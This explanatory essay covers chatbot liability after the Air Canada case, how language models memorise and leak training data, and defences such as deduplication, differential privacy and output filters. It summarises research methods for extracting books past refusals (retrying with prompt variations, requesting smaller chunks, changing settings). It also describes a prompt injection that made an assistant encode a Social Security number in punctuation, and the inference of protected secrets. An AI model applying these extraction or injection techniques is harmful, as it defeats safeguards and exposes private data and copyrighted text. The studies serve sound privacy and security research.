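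The case is more famous than its legal authority warrants. Hedley (2024), in *Moffatt v. Air Canada, 2024 BCCRT 149*, calls it a low-level decision that analyses the problem rather superficially. Business Law Today concedes that it isn't a court decision but still reads it as a reminder that companies are liable for their AI tools. That reading seems right for an ordinary customer with an ordinary question, but it is much less secure for large commercial contracts, where both sides have lawyers and are expected to read the terms.

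The same five-part test works against a user who manipulates a bot. Someone who spends an hour persuading the shop's assistant to promise a free laptop will struggle to show that they reasonably relied on the promise. Haggling is harder to judge. A customer who asks for 10% off and gets it has done nothing that would be improper with a human salesperson, and can fairly assume that the shop lets its assistant give discounts.

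### Labels, policies and people

The application's own code should add the AI label, so that nothing the model writes can remove it. On a phone call, the application has to speak the label. In an email, the label should be part of the sender's name and the signature, so that it stays visible when someone forwards the message or posts a screenshot. Gausen and colleagues point out that a company can leave labels out. Still, a permanent label is easy to add and is an adequate safeguard when a chatbot has a human name. If the model claims to be human, the label at least contradicts it.

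Telling customers that they are talking to a bot doesn't prevent it from giving them a false refund rule. It also doesn't stop users who manipulate the bot, since they already know what it is. Some companies warn that answers may contain mistakes, but this is hard to reconcile with Rivers's view that customers shouldn't have to check one part of a website against another.

To prevent invented policies, the shop can store its rules as numbered passages, let the model choose a number, and have the application display that passage word for word. This suits statements about refunds, prices and accounts. Sam's rule could not have appeared as a quoted policy, because no such passage existed. Letting the model paraphrase the policy is a weaker protection, and so is providing a link, as the Air Canada case showed. Even with fixed passages, the model can choose the wrong one. Any free text around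 the passage can also contradict it, so the application should show as little of that text as possible on these subjects.

Companies can also deny the bot any authority to bind them. They can say so in their terms, which gives them a contractual defence, though a consumer may never have seen those terms. Or they can apply least privilege, so that the application takes prices from the catalogue, refuses refunds above a limit and sends exceptions to an employee. A minimum price enforced outside the model would have kept Claudius from selling tungsten at a loss, however persuasive its customers were. But such limits govern only what the system does, so the model can still promise something the system won't carry out, and an honest customer may spend money because of that promise.

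Anything outside the approved passages and limits should go to a person who can see what the bot has already written. On the day of the first booking, an Air Canada employee told Moffatt over the phone that the bereavement fare would be about $380 each way. There is no evidence that the employee mentioned claiming the fare afterwards. If the employee had seen the chatbot's answer, they could have corrected it five days before Moffatt bought the return ticket.

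## Why do models repeat training data, and how is it measured?

Air Canada's chatbot gave Jake Moffatt a false refund rule. A model can also do harm by accurately reproducing a passage from its training data, such as a chapter of a novel or somebody's private letter. It is hard to measure how much training data a model has stored, because a model that writes fluent English will sometimes match an existing text without having stored it.

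### How training stores a passage

A language model consists of billions of numbers, called weights or parameters. During training, the model estimates the probability of each possible next token in a piece of text, and a program adjusts the weights slightly to make the actual next token more probable. Most of these adjustments capture patterns common to many texts. For example, after "The dog barked at the", a model may give "cat" a higher probability than "chair" or "moon" (Lemley and Cooper, 2026, *Probabilistic "Copies" in Generative AI Models*).

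Training reinforces both general patterns and the wording of particular texts, because both help predict the next token. If a passage appears often enough in the training data, each of its tokens can make the next one almost certain, though the model still assigns some probability to other continuations. Lemley and Cooper compare this to a loaded die that lands on three 95% of the time.

The weights then contain the passage in the sense that the model can generate it. Nobody can locate it in the weights the way they could find a file on a disk, and even the developers typically don't know which texts their model has retained.

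### Repetition, size and timing

*Quantifying Memorization Across Neural Language Models* (Carlini, Lee and colleagues, 2022) finds that a model is more likely to repeat a passage when the model has more parameters, the training data contains more copies of the passage, or the prompt is longer. Each relationship is log-linear, so every doubling adds roughly the same amount, whether from 10 copies to 20 or from 100 to 200. *Memorization in Language Models through the Lens of Intrinsic Dimension* (2025) confirms the pattern for copies and model size, and adds that among rarely repeated passages, models memorise the structurally complex ones less.

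Comparing existing models can't fully separate these causes, since a sentence that appears often may also be a simple one. Wei, Godbole and colleagues (2025), in *Hubble*, addressed this by training their own models on ordinary web text into which they had inserted book passages, biographies and test questions. They randomly assigned each item to appear 0, 1, 4, 16, 64 or 256 times. Their models with 8 billion parameters memorised items after fewer repetitions than those with 1 billion. The same number of copies led to weaker memorisation in a training set of 500 billion tokens than in one of 100 billion, so memorisation depends on how often a text appears relative to the rest of the training data.

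Timing also affected memorisation. The finished model had forgotten items that the researchers inserted only during the first quarter of training, and it remembered items from the last quarter better than items spread over the whole run. *Don't Forget! Decomposing the Training Dynamics of Memorization in Language Models* (2026) seems to conflict with this, since it found that much of the memorisation in the Pythia family of models happens early. Both findings can be true if a passage that keeps recurring becomes extractable early and stays extractable, while a passage that stops appearing is gradually forgotten.

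### The 50-token test

A model memorises training text when its weights store a particular passage, so that the model gives that passage unusually high probability. Extraction means getting the model to reproduce the passage in its output. Researchers can't look up a passage in the weights, so they usually infer memorisation from extraction.

In the standard test, researchers take 100 tokens from a document they know was in the training data and give the model the first 50. The model continues the text, always choosing the most probable next token, which is known as greedy decoding. The test succeeds if the next 50 tokens the model generates (about 37 English words) match the document exactly.

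A failed attempt to make a model repeat training data proves little, because a different prompt might have worked. *Detecting Functional Memorization in Code Language Models* (2026) explains that researchers therefore now distinguish "discoverable" from "extractable" text. Memorised text is discoverable if the model produces it when given the exact words that preceded it in training, and extractable if at least one prompt makes the model produce it. Testing whether text is discoverable requires already having the document, so the test measures what a model has stored more directly than what someone without the document could learn from it.

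Wei and colleagues show that an exact-match test can miss memorization. Their 8-billion-parameter model with the smaller training set assigned measurably higher probability to Wikipedia passages inserted four times into that set than to passages it had never seen. A difference in verbatim reproduction appeared only at 16 copies.

### From token probabilities to the number of tries

The applications that people use rarely choose the most probable token every time. They draw tokens at random in proportion to their probabilities, so the same prompt can give different answers. To reproduce a passage, the model has to draw the right token at every step, and the probability of that is the product of the individual probabilities:

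`q = p₁ × p₂ × … × p₅₀`

Each *p* is the probability of one token, given the prompt and all the correct tokens before it. If someone tries *n* times with the same prompt, the chance of at least one success is one minus the chance of failing every time:

`1 − (1 − q)ⁿ`

If each of the 50 tokens has a probability of 0.9, *q* is 0.9⁵⁰, or about 0.005, which is roughly one success in 200 tries. *Characterizing Memorization in Diffusion Language Models* (Luo, Yu and colleagues, 2026) rearranges the second formula to give the number of tries needed, *n* = log(1 − *c*) / log(1 − *q*), where *c* is the desired chance of success. For a 90% chance, *n* is about 446.

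| Probability of each token | Chance of all 50 in one try | Tries for a 90% chance |
|---|---|---|
| 0.8 | 0.000014 | About 161,000 |
| 0.9 | 0.005 | 446 |
| 0.95 | 0.08 | 29 |
| 0.99 | 0.6 | 3 |

Small differences in the model's certainty therefore determine whether a passage is practically safe or appears almost every time someone asks for it. They also explain why greedy decoding, the standard test, can overstate or understate the risk. A token with a probability of 0.9 is always the most probable one, so the test would reproduce the passage in the second row every time, though an ordinary user would see it about once in 200 attempts. But if a single token in the passage is slightly less probable than an alternative, greedy decoding never produces the passage, while random sampling often might.

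Longer passages are harder to extract whole. Even if a model has a 0.99 probability of reproducing each token correctly, it has only about one chance in 23,000 of reproducing a 1,000-token passage in full. An attacker who wants a long text is better off asking for it in pieces.

These formulas suit models that generate text from left to right, as most do. Diffusion language models instead fill in masked words over several rounds. Luo and colleagues found that these models generally reproduce training text more often when they fill in fewer words per round, because each correct word then helps the model predict more of the remaining ones.

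### GPT-2 and ChatGPT

In 2021 Nicholas Carlini and colleagues extracted verbatim training text from OpenAI's GPT-2. *Detecting Functional Memorization in Code Language Models* credits their study as the first to do this with an LLM. Luo and colleagues describe the early evidence as hundreds of verbatim sequences, some of them rare and sensitive, that an outsider could obtain just by querying the model. Much of what GPT-2 repeated was more mundane, such as software licences and other text found across the web.

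Training ChatGPT to answer questions made its memorised text harder to extract but didn't remove it from the weights. If a user types the first half of a paragraph, a chatbot tends to comment on it or ask what the user wants, so the 50-token test mostly fails. In 2023 Milad Nasr and colleagues found that a simple, repetitive prompt could make an earlier version of ChatGPT stop responding this way and produce training text unrelated to the prompt. They didn't have OpenAI's training data, so they counted only runs of at least 50 tokens that exactly matched a large collection of web text the model had probably seen. The longest run was slightly over 4,000 characters.

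### Whole books from commercial models

In August and September 2025, Ahmed, Cooper and colleagues tested four commercial models for long copyrighted works, which Nasr's team had not looked for. They tried thirteen books, eleven of which are under copyright in the United States. They published *Extracting books from production language models* in January 2026, after giving the companies 90 days' notice.

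The researchers first gave the model a sentence or so from the start of a book and asked it to continue word for word. If it did, they kept asking for more until it refused, it reached the end or the budget ran out. They supplied no further text from the book, so everything after the opening came from the model. Gemini 2.5 Pro and Grok 3 complied immediately. Claude 3.7 Sonnet and GPT-4.1 did not, so the researchers resubmitted the request with random variations until the model complied.

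The researchers counted only near-exact passages of at least 100 words, in the right order. The table shows their results for *Harry Potter and the Sorcerer's Stone*.

| Model | Share of the book recovered | Variations needed to start | Longest passage, in words | Cost of continuing |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 95.8% | 258 | 6,658 | $119.97 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 76.8% | 0 | 9,070 | $2.44 |
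| Grok 3 | 70.3% | 0 | 6,337 | $8.16 |
| GPT-4.1 | 4.0% | 5,179 | 821 | $1.37 |

Claude also reproduced nearly all of *1984* and two public-domain novels, *Frankenstein* and *The Great Gatsby*. But most of the experiments recovered 10% of a book or less, and none of the four models could continue the opening of one novel, *The Duchess War*.

The safeguards slowed extraction and sometimes cut it short. Gemini's service at times returned an empty reply with a notice about reciting copyrighted material, but changing the settings mostly avoided this. Claude stopped refusing once the researchers asked for less text at a time. GPT-4.1 resisted extraction most and always stopped by the end of the first chapter, but it sometimes fulfilled a request it had earlier refused. The researchers recovered more text by starting afresh at each chapter and retrying after refusals, which shows that the model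 had memorised text beyond the point where it first stopped.

To check that the models were reproducing memorized text, Ahmed and colleagues tried a novel published on July 31, 2025, too late for any of the four to have trained on it. None could continue its opening. This was only one control book, but it seems very unlikely that a model would produce thousands of consecutive words of *Harry Potter* by chance.

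The percentages don't give a fair ranking of the four companies, because the researchers tuned the settings separately for each model and mostly report one run per book. They also mainly chose books that an open model, Llama 3.1 70B, was already known to have memorised. All four models are now old, and Claude 3.7 Sonnet was no longer available in Anthropic's chat application by the end of November 2025. Ahmed and colleagues quote an earlier paper's remark that "there are easier and more effective ways to pirate a book," so the result matters more for text that nobody can buy or download elsewhere.

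### What comes out without an attack

These researchers all tried to extract training text. In *LLMs Can Leak Training Data But Do They Want To?*, Barmina, Schneider-Kamp and Galke Poech (2026) measured how often models produce training text when nobody is trying to extract it. They used three models whose complete training data is public, and searched that data for every stretch of text the models produced. The table gives the share of outputs that contained at least 50 consecutive tokens of training text.

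| What the model received | Outputs with a long match |
|---|---|
| An everyday sentence | 0.4–0.9% |
| A new sentence resembling the training data | 1.4–2.8% |
| The first 50 tokens of a training document | 9.0–13.6% |
| Nothing | 1.9–41.4% |

Everyday sentences used as prompts rarely led models to copy long passages of training data, although the risk grows with use. When the researchers drew ten outputs for each sentence, between 3.3% and 7.2% of the sentences produced at least one long copy.

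The highest rates came from models given no prompt. Most of the repeated text was harmless boilerplate, such as licences, web-page templates and coding exercises, which appear many times in the training data. But 6.6% of one model's unprompted outputs contained a long passage that appears only once in the training set.

Barmina and colleagues tested base models, which haven't had the further training that turns a model into a chatbot. That training could raise or lower the rates, so the figures don't carry over to commercial assistants. Their test sentences also weren't real user requests. A request that mentions a book by title falls between the second and third rows, a case they didn't test.

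### When a match is only a good guess

An encyclopedia article about a politician might begin a sentence with the person's name and date of birth. A capable model can often complete the sentence correctly because it was trained on thousands like it, even if it was never trained on this one. A test that uses only training text counts every such success as memorisation.

Prompts can also make a model's output look memorised when it isn't. If a user asks a chatbot to repeat a sentence, it will do so whether or not the sentence was in its training data. *Extractable Memorization from First Principles* (Cooper, Swanberg and colleagues, July 2026) gives a subtler case. Researchers had previously searched for an unusual short prompt that would make a model produce a given quotation, and treated success as evidence of memorisation. This method worked on a famous line by the hockey player Wayne Gretzky,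 but Cooper and colleagues got it to work equally well on a remark that a basketball player made in 2026, long after the model's training had ended.

To account for this, researchers run the same procedure on matched control passages, which the model can't have seen but which resemble the training passages in source, format and length. The model's success on these controls can't come from memorisation, so it shows how often the model can succeed just because text is predictable.

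Cooper and colleagues turn this into a statistical procedure called a conformal test. It begins by giving every passage a score, for example the probability *q* that the model will produce it. For a suspected training passage, the test then calculates

`(1 + number of controls that score at least as high) / (N + 1)`

where *N* is the number of controls. With 999 controls, none of which reaches the suspect's score, the result is 1/1,000. If the suspect were really an unseen passage of the same kind, it would be equally likely to take any place in a ranking of all 1,000 passages. It would therefore come first only once in 1,000 times. A researcher decides beforehand how often a false alarm is acceptable, say 1% of the time, and claims memorisation only if the result is no higher than that. The test doesn't make the opposite claim, because a passage with a low score may still be in the weights.

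The controls also guard against misleading prompts. If a prompt makes the model repeat anything it receives, the controls score as high as the suspected training data, so nothing is counted as memorized.

Cooper and colleagues tested OLMo 2 32B, an open model whose training data is public. They took 5,000 Wikipedia passages from before the end of its training and 5,000 from articles dated 2024, gave the model 50 tokens of each, and asked for the next 10. The model reproduced those 10 tokens for 7.54% of the training passages. The false-positive floor, the rate at which the test would flag text the model had never seen, was 1.84%. That is 24% of the first figure, so about a quarter of the apparent extractions may just be predictable text, though the calculation can't identify which ones.

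In the 50-token test, the model reproduced only 0.74% of the training passages, but the floor, measured on control passages, fell to 0.04%. Even that floor was too high, because it came from a single control passage that turned out to contain text from the training data. The longer test therefore finds fewer matches, but they are much more credible.

The choice of controls is the weak point. Articles from 2024 may cover people and events that the model knows nothing about, which would make them harder to predict for reasons unrelated to memorisation. The true floor would then be higher than 1.84%. Cooper and colleagues accept that the guarantee depends on how closely the controls match the training text. Some texts, such as Arthur Conan Doyle's Sherlock Holmes stories, have no good match because there are no new stories by the same author to use as controls.

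### Five-word matches and lawsuits

Courts can now use these measurements in copyright cases. Lemley and Cooper count more than a hundred pending lawsuits that accuse AI companies of infringement. In November 2025 a German court held that ChatGPT contained a copy of certain song lyrics, while an English court rejected a similar argument about an image generator.

*Alignment Whack-a-Mole* reports that commercial models could reproduce up to 85–90% of a book after fine-tuning (further training on a smaller set of texts). Possible plaintiffs wanted to cite this figure, but in September 2026 A. Feder Cooper, a co-author of several of the studies described here, publicly criticised how it was measured. Cooper objects that it counts any run of five consecutive words that appears in both an output and the book (*Playing Whack-a-Mole with misconceptions about memorization, extraction, and copyright*,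 2026).

The procedure splits the book into excerpts, gives the model a detailed summary of each, and collects 100 outputs per excerpt. For a book of 300 excerpts, that makes 30,000 outputs, about 100 times as much text as the book. In that much text, many five-word runs will match by chance. A phrase such as "two cups on the table" counts wherever it occurs in the book, even if only one output contained it. The original researchers removed five-word runs that also appeared in the prompt, but a close summary may still steer the model towards the book's phrasing. According to Cooper, they reported no control experiment that would show how much of the total is due to chance.

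This criticism of the 85–90% figure is convincing, but it doesn't show that the models had memorised little. Cooper accepts that the same work contains genuine extractions hundreds of words long, and thinks it very plausible that fine-tuning can reveal huge amounts of memorised text. Testing recent books by the same authors as a control would largely settle how much the figure overstates memorisation.

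Neither side of such disputes is entirely detached. Cooper helped develop the rival measures, and Mark Lemley, a co-author on several of these papers, has represented AI companies in copyright cases. But the argument about short matches doesn't depend on anyone's motives, because the Wikipedia controls show the problem directly.

### Memorised but out of reach

Cooper and colleagues ran a matched comparison on whole books with Llama 3.1 70B. They paired each of four books from the training data with a newer book by the same author, published after the model's training ended. For example, they paired *The Hunger Games* with its prequel *Sunrise on the Reaping*. They then slid a window along each book, gave the model 50 tokens at a time, and calculated the probability that it would produce the next 50.

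The researchers used the highest probability in the newer book as the threshold for the older one. They first had to remove quotations from older works, because the prequel repeatedly quotes Edgar Allan Poe's "The Raven", which the model may well have memorized. The remaining thresholds ranged from 10⁻²¹ to 10⁻²⁷.

A probability of 10⁻²⁷ for 50 tokens is tiny, but it corresponds to an average of about 0.29 per token, which is quite high for a model with a vocabulary of about 128,000 tokens. The model did not assign a higher probability than that to any passage in the newer book. If it does so for a passage from the older book, the most likely explanation is that the passage was in its training data.

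By this standard, the model had memorised 68.5% of *The Da Vinci Code*, 53.3% of *The Hunger Games*, 31.3% of *We Were Eight Years in Power* and almost none of the fourth book, *Killer Instinct*. A threshold based on a single newer book has no guaranteed error rate, but the result for *The Da Vinci Code* doesn't depend much on the exact threshold. When the researchers required probabilities 100,000 times higher, 55.6% of the book still passed.

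An attacker who can only query the model cannot realistically extract most of this text. If the model produces a passage with probability 10⁻²¹, the attacker needs about 3 × 10²¹ tries for a 95% chance of seeing it at least once. At a thousand tries per second, that would take nearly seven times the age of the universe. With a more realistic 100,000 tries per passage, the attacker could extract only 12.3% of *The Da Vinci Code* word for word.

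Cooper and colleagues therefore propose calling a passage "extractably memorised" only if it both passes the matched comparison and is almost certain to appear within a realistic number of tries. The second condition matters most for security, though a copyright court might care more about the first if it has to decide whether the model itself contains a copy.

Which training data an attacker can extract also depends on their access to the model. Someone who has downloaded an open model can control how it chooses tokens and follow many promising continuations at once, which commercial services generally don't allow. Researchers used such a method to extract nearly all of *Harry Potter and the Sorcerer's Stone* from Llama 3.1 70B, starting from a short piece of the opening.

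### Near-verbatim copies

An exact-match test misses a copied passage if the model writes a hyphen where the book has a dash, even though a reader or a judge would consider the two passages the same.

In *Estimating near-verbatim extraction risk in language models with decoding-constrained beam search* (2026), Cooper, Lemley and colleagues allow for such differences by counting edits. A 50-token continuation counts as near-verbatim if at most five insertions, deletions or substitutions would turn it into the original. The risk for a passage is the combined probability of all continuations that qualify.

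There are far too many of these variants to check. Even two substitutions, with a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens, give more than a trillion. Sampling isn't much better, since it takes about 100,000 samples to reliably estimate the probability of a passage that has a one-in-a-thousand chance of being generated. The researchers instead use beam search, which keeps the 20 most probable partial continuations at each step. They then add up the probabilities of the finished continuations that are close enough to the original. The search may miss some variants, so the total is a lower bound, but it takes only about as much computation as 20 samples.

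This works because the model assigns a high probability to nearly every token of a passage it has memorised. For a 50-token passage to have even a one-in-a-thousand chance of being generated, its tokens must have an average probability of at least about 0.87, and at most three of them can be as low as 0.1. A search that stays close to the model's top choices will therefore find most of the memorised text that the model has a realistic chance of producing.

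An older Llama model assigned a probability of 0.14 to the exact text of one passage from *The Great Gatsby*. The standard test would have recorded a failure to reproduce the passage, because the model's most probable continuation differed slightly from the book. The total probability of the exact text and its close variants was at least 0.72.

The researchers tested 10,000 Wikipedia passages from OLMo 2 32B's training data and counted a passage as extractable if the model had at least a one-in-a-thousand chance of producing it. By this measure, 1.42% were extractable word for word, and 2.57% when close variants counted. The usual method, greedy decoding with exact matching, found only 0.61%. Rates stayed near zero for articles written after the model's training, so lucky guesses alone don't explain the increase from counting close variants.

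The gap widens as models grow. In *The Great Gatsby*, 76 passages were extractable only in near-verbatim form from the smallest Llama 2 model, compared with 1,606 from the largest, which has ten times as many parameters. About 80% of those 1,606 could not appear word for word under the sampling rule used, so a filter that blocks only exact copies would miss them.

Five edits in 50 tokens is a reasonable allowance for a novel, where a changed comma makes no difference to the reader. It is less suitable for text such as phone numbers and passwords, where a single wrong character can give someone else's number or a password that doesn't work.

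## How much private data can be drawn from a model, and what limits it?

An LLM application holds private data in the model's weights and in its context. The weights hold whatever the model memorised in training and are the same for every user. The context holds what the application supplies for one request, including saved memories about the user and retrieved files. For example, a stranger's phone number from an old web page may be in the weights, while the number of a customer chatting with a shop's assistant is in the context.

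An application can drop a file from the context before the next request, but removing anything from the weights is hard. However, a model can copy a password from its context after seeing it once, without having to memorise it.

### Memory or a good guess?

If a model gives Anna Keller's email address as "anna.keller" followed by a popular mail domain, it may have memorised the address or guessed it, since many addresses follow that pattern.

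In *Do LLMs Really Memorize Personally Identifiable Information?*, Luo, Chen and colleagues (2026) tried to separate the two. They tested three models with public training data and up to 13 billion parameters, using email addresses and phone numbers from web pages in 32 languages. They distinguish three kinds of memorisation by what the prompt contains, and define "extractable" more narrowly than usual, allowing only general requests. The table shows the results for the largest model.

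| Kind of memorisation | What the model receives | Email addresses | Phone numbers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Verbatim | The 100 tokens before the item in the training data | 1.08% recovered | 0.23% recovered |
| Associative | The person's name, sometimes with another contact detail | 0.06% recovered | Under 0.01% recovered |
| Extractable | A general request for a list | 0.29% of those generated were real | 0.28% of those generated were real |

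The researchers then measured how much of each answer was already in the prompt. They took the longest string of characters that the prompt and the answer share, and divided its length by the length of the answer. If a page lists a fax number as 555-0142 and the phone number is 555-0143, the overlap is six digits out of seven, or 0.86. The average overlap was 0.85 for the phone numbers that the largest model recovered verbatim and 0.18 for those it missed. When the prompt contained less than half of an email address, the model almost never completed it.

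The best evidence that the model was guessing rather than remembering comes from another 16,826 samples whose email addresses were not in the training data. When the hints were equally strong, the model got these addresses right about as often as those it had trained on. A few recoveries look like memory, though, including a Belarusian email address that had no overlap with its prompt and an English phone number with an overlap of only 0.20.

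Luo and colleagues call leakage without hints negligible. That fairly describes the rate, but the largest model still produced 2,074 real phone numbers in 640,000 answers to general requests. An attacker couldn't tell which numbers were real or whose they were, and some may have matched real numbers by chance.

Another experiment found more leakage without a hint. *On the Privacy of LLMs* (2026) describes prompting GPT-J-6B, an open model, 5,000 times with a blank email header, which contains no name to guess from. On average, the replies contained 374 different addresses from its training data, which included the emails of the energy company Enron. Addresses recur constantly in a company's mail, so the Enron emails are probably much easier to extract from than ordinary web pages.

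### API keys

An API key is a long random string that identifies a customer to an online service, and anyone who has it can use the service at the customer's expense. Programmers often leave keys in published code by mistake. A model can't work out a key from its owner's name, so a real key in its output is very unlikely to be a guess.

Zhao, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *Practical Secrets Extraction Against Black-Box LLMs*, tried to recover keys from models while seeing only their output. They collected 100 keys from each of five providers (OpenAI, OpenRouter, Google, DeepSeek and Stripe), placed them in snippets of code, and fine-tuned three open models on those snippets. Two of the models were specialised in coding. The table gives the average number of keys recovered per hundred, with the better of two versions of the paper's new method.

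| Model fine-tuned on the keys | HCR, an earlier method | Greedy decoding | New method |
|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-Coder-7B | 27.4 | 28.0 | 35.0 |
| Qwen2.5-Coder-7B | 29.6 | 30.0 | 35.0 |
| LLaMA-3-8B | 44.2 | 44.2 | 49.4 |

Taking the model's most probable answer recovers most of the keys, and the new method adds five to seven per hundred. The paper reports an improvement of up to 57.1% in its introduction but up to 25.0% in its conclusion. The averages support the lower figure. Most candidate keys were fake. In one set of tests, about 24% of candidate Google keys were real, up from roughly 10% with DESEC, an earlier method that uses token probabilities. For OpenAI keys, the share was only about 2%.

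These models had just been trained on the keys the researchers were looking for. The benchmark therefore measures how well an attacker can recover keys that a model has recently learned, but provides little evidence of how many keys a commercial model has memorised. It is most relevant to a company that fine-tunes a model on its own code.

The researchers also gave one code prompt to three models already in use. Qwen3-27B returned two DeepSeek keys and a Google key, GPT-Codex 5.3 returned one DeepSeek key, and Claude Haiku 4.5 returned two. A GitHub search found all six in public code. Strings that long don't match by accident, so this is good evidence that a commercial model can output keys from public code. But six examples don't show how often this happens, and the keys were already available to anyone searching GitHub. For ethical reasons, the researchers didn't check whether the keys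 still worked.

The two studies are compatible. Models of moderate size seem to retain few personal details that appear only once or twice on the web, but a model can reproduce in full a string that recurs or that a company fine-tunes it on.

### The number a model avoids

A model's outputs can reveal a secret in its context without stating it. Fairoze, Mangaokar and colleagues (2026), in *Inadvertent Context Leakage in Language Models*, gave eight commercial models a secret number and told them never to reveal it, hint at it or encode it. The models refused all 160 direct requests. The researchers then asked for unrelated things, such as a list of random numbers, and tried to infer the secret from the answers.

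A model told to protect a number tends to avoid it, which can reveal the number. If 500 two-digit numbers are drawn at random with equal probability, any particular number has less than a 1% chance of never appearing, so a missing one stands out. Models don't draw numbers evenly, and longer secrets leave subtler traces. The researchers therefore gave each model secrets they had chosen themselves and trained a small second model to recognise how those secrets affected its answers.

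| Length of the secret | Highest recovery | Other models |
|---|---|---|
| 1 digit | 100% on six of the eight models | Grok 4.1 Fast 99%, GPT-5.4 nano 37% |
| 2 digits | Whole number: Claude Opus 4.6 and Gemini 3.1 Pro 100% | Individual digits: GPT-5.4 99.5%, Claude Sonnet 4.6 98.5%, Grok 4 94.5% |
| 4 digits | Whole number: Claude Opus 4.6 82%, Gemini 3.1 Pro 44% | Individual digits: GPT-5.4 63%; Grok 4.1 Fast and GPT-5.4 nano no better than guessing |
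| 8 digits | Individual digits: Gemini 3.1 Pro 41%, where guessing gives 10% | First digit only: Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite 93%, GPT-5.4 nano 19% |

These are best-case figures, because each comes from the prompt and inference method that worked best for that model and length. A real attacker would have to choose both in advance. The two-digit test was also easier than it looks, because every number in it had appeared in the second model's training. Very few of the four-digit numbers had, so the 82% is more impressive.

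The attack works only if the attacker knows which model the victim uses and how long the secret is, and if the instructions single out a particular value to protect. Requests for lists of numbers leaked the most, while open-ended requests and ordinary conversation leaked almost nothing, so an assistant that only drafts emails would be a poor target for this version of the attack.

Stricter instructions can make the leak worse. When a short request told Claude Opus 4.6 to keep the number private, the researchers guessed its digits no better than chance, but with a long confidentiality policy they recovered 64% of them. Gemini 3.1 Pro leaked under every wording. When the context contained several numbers of the same length, the researchers could recover only the protected one. Across the eight models, those that avoided the secret more also leaked more, but this mostly reflects the gap between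 leaky and resistant models.

Fairoze and colleagues also tested whether routine answers reveal which memories about a user, such as a health condition, were in the context. They trained a classifier on Claude Opus 4.6's answers and compared it with a model that looked for the memories in the text. At the same false-alarm rate of 2.4%, the classifier detected 14.0% of the memories present, and the comparison model detected 8.2%. The test covered a single user's profile and showed only that a memory was present, which leaks much less than its full contents would.

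### A Social Security number in an agent's files

The most realistic of these experiments used a personal assistant whose memory file contained a nine-digit US Social Security number. The researchers used prompt injection to make the assistant encode each digit in the punctuation of an otherwise harmless message, rather than relying on accidental traces.

Each of the two models went through 70 trials, with up to 256,000 tokens of other material in the context. Claude Opus 4.6 revealed the first digit in 68 trials and the remaining eight in 52 of those, so the whole number leaked in 74% of all trials. Gemini 3.1 Pro revealed the first digit in 62 trials and the rest in 29 of those, so the whole number leaked in 41%. Neither model disclosed the number in 350 direct requests, so a company that tests its assistant only by asking for the secret would have considered both safe.

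Fairoze and colleagues collected the main results on numbers in April 2026, and newer models have since replaced several of those they tested. They were able to test OLMo-3-32B-Think, an open model, after each stage of training, and found that it leaked more after it had learned to follow instructions, although training could plausibly have reduced the leakage.

### Cleaning the training data

Repetition strengthens memorisation, so developers can reduce memorisation by removing duplicates before training. CNIL's *Analysing the status of an AI model with regard to the GDPR* (2026), guidance from France's data protection authority, recommends removing both exact duplicates and near-duplicates, such as copies of a web page that differ only in the date. It also recommends deleting identifying details and rare records, which a model tends to memorise first.

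Developers sometimes repeat training documents on purpose. The training mixture for Google's Gemma 2 models, for example, repeats some documents from better sources up to seven times. Removing duplicate documents also doesn't protect a family's address that appears on hundreds of different pages.

API keys are easier to remove than most personal data, because each provider's keys have a typical length and often a fixed opening. A scanner can find them, though it will miss passwords that look like ordinary words. Unlike a diagnosis, a leaked key can also be cancelled by its owner, which makes the memorised copy useless.

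### Differential privacy

Differential privacy limits how much any one piece of training data can affect the finished model. During training, the program caps the influence of each example on the weights and adds random noise, so that no single example makes much difference. The guarantee is

`P(outcome, trained with the example) ≤ e^ε × P(outcome, trained without it) + δ`

and it holds for every possible outcome, including an attacker naming a particular secret. Smaller values of ε and δ give stronger protection.

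Google trained a one-billion-parameter model with differential privacy from the start. *VaultGemma* (2025) reports a guarantee of ε ≤ 2.0 and δ ≤ 1.1 × 10⁻¹⁰ for each sequence of 1,024 tokens. Since e² is about 7.4, training on a sequence can raise the probability of any outcome to at most 7.4 times what it would be without that sequence, plus δ. If a random API key appears in only one sequence, an attacker would have practically no chance of guessing it from a model trained without that sequence. Multiplying that chance by 7.4 still leaves it near zero, so the attacker's chance of extracting the key is at most about δ, or one in nine billion, however many questions they ask.

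The guarantee covers one sequence, so it weakens when text is repeated. If the same text appears in seven sequences, ε becomes 14 and the factor rises to about 1.2 million. In the worst case, that could raise the chance of guessing a phone number from one in ten million to about one in eight. Differential privacy therefore works best after a developer has removed duplicates.

In the 50-token test, run on about a million training samples, the researchers found no memorisation in VaultGemma, even counting near matches, whereas every Gemma model trained without differential privacy showed some. Training with differential privacy also made VaultGemma much less capable, roughly on par with ordinary models from five years earlier. It scored 11.2 on TriviaQA, a test of factual questions, against 39.8 for Gemma 3 with the same number of parameters. Much of this loss may be unavoidable, because the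 training program can't distinguish an obscure fact that appears in only one document from a private detail.

A company can limit differential privacy to fine-tuning, which is far cheaper than training a model from scratch. This protects the company's own data but not what the model memorised earlier, and it reduces accuracy. *Frequency-Conditioned Privacy Auditing of Fine-Tuned Language Models* (2026) reports that the accuracy of Llama 3.2 1B on MNLI, a test of whether one sentence follows from another, fell from 79.5% to 48.3% at an ε of 8 and to 46.2% at an ε of 3. Most of the loss came from using differential privacy at all, so a company that accepts the accuracy at an ε of 8 may as well consider the stronger privacy at an ε of 3.

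### Output filters and unlearning

An output filter checks the model's answer for known secrets or training text before anyone sees it. The simplest kind looks for exact matches, so it misses a phone number with different spacing, a password with dashes between its letters, or a paragraph with one changed word.

A better filter ignores spaces and punctuation, or blocks any text within a certain number of edits of a protected passage. Looser matching also blocks more harmless answers. An attacker can still ask for the secret in another alphabet or spread over several answers. If the filter visibly blocks an answer, the attacker learns that a guess was right.

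In the Social Security test, a filter looking for the nine digits might have stopped Claude Opus 4.6, which wrote the number openly in 69 of 70 trials while working out how to encode it. Gemini 3.1 Pro never wrote the number openly, so the same filter would have missed it. A filter also has nothing to match in the case of the avoided numbers, because the evidence is in what the model leaves out. Nor do filters help once someone has downloaded an open model, because that person can run it without them.

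Unlearning means changing a trained model so that it no longer contains particular data. The dependable way is to retrain the model without that data, which is very expensive for a large model. Faster methods adjust the existing weights, but a model that has stopped producing a passage may still contain it. ChatGPT, for example, still contained passages that it had stopped producing after its chatbot training. Privacy World (2026), a law-firm blog, interprets recent draft guidance from the European Data Protection Board (EDPB) as accepting that developers cannot yet easily make a model unlearn particular data.

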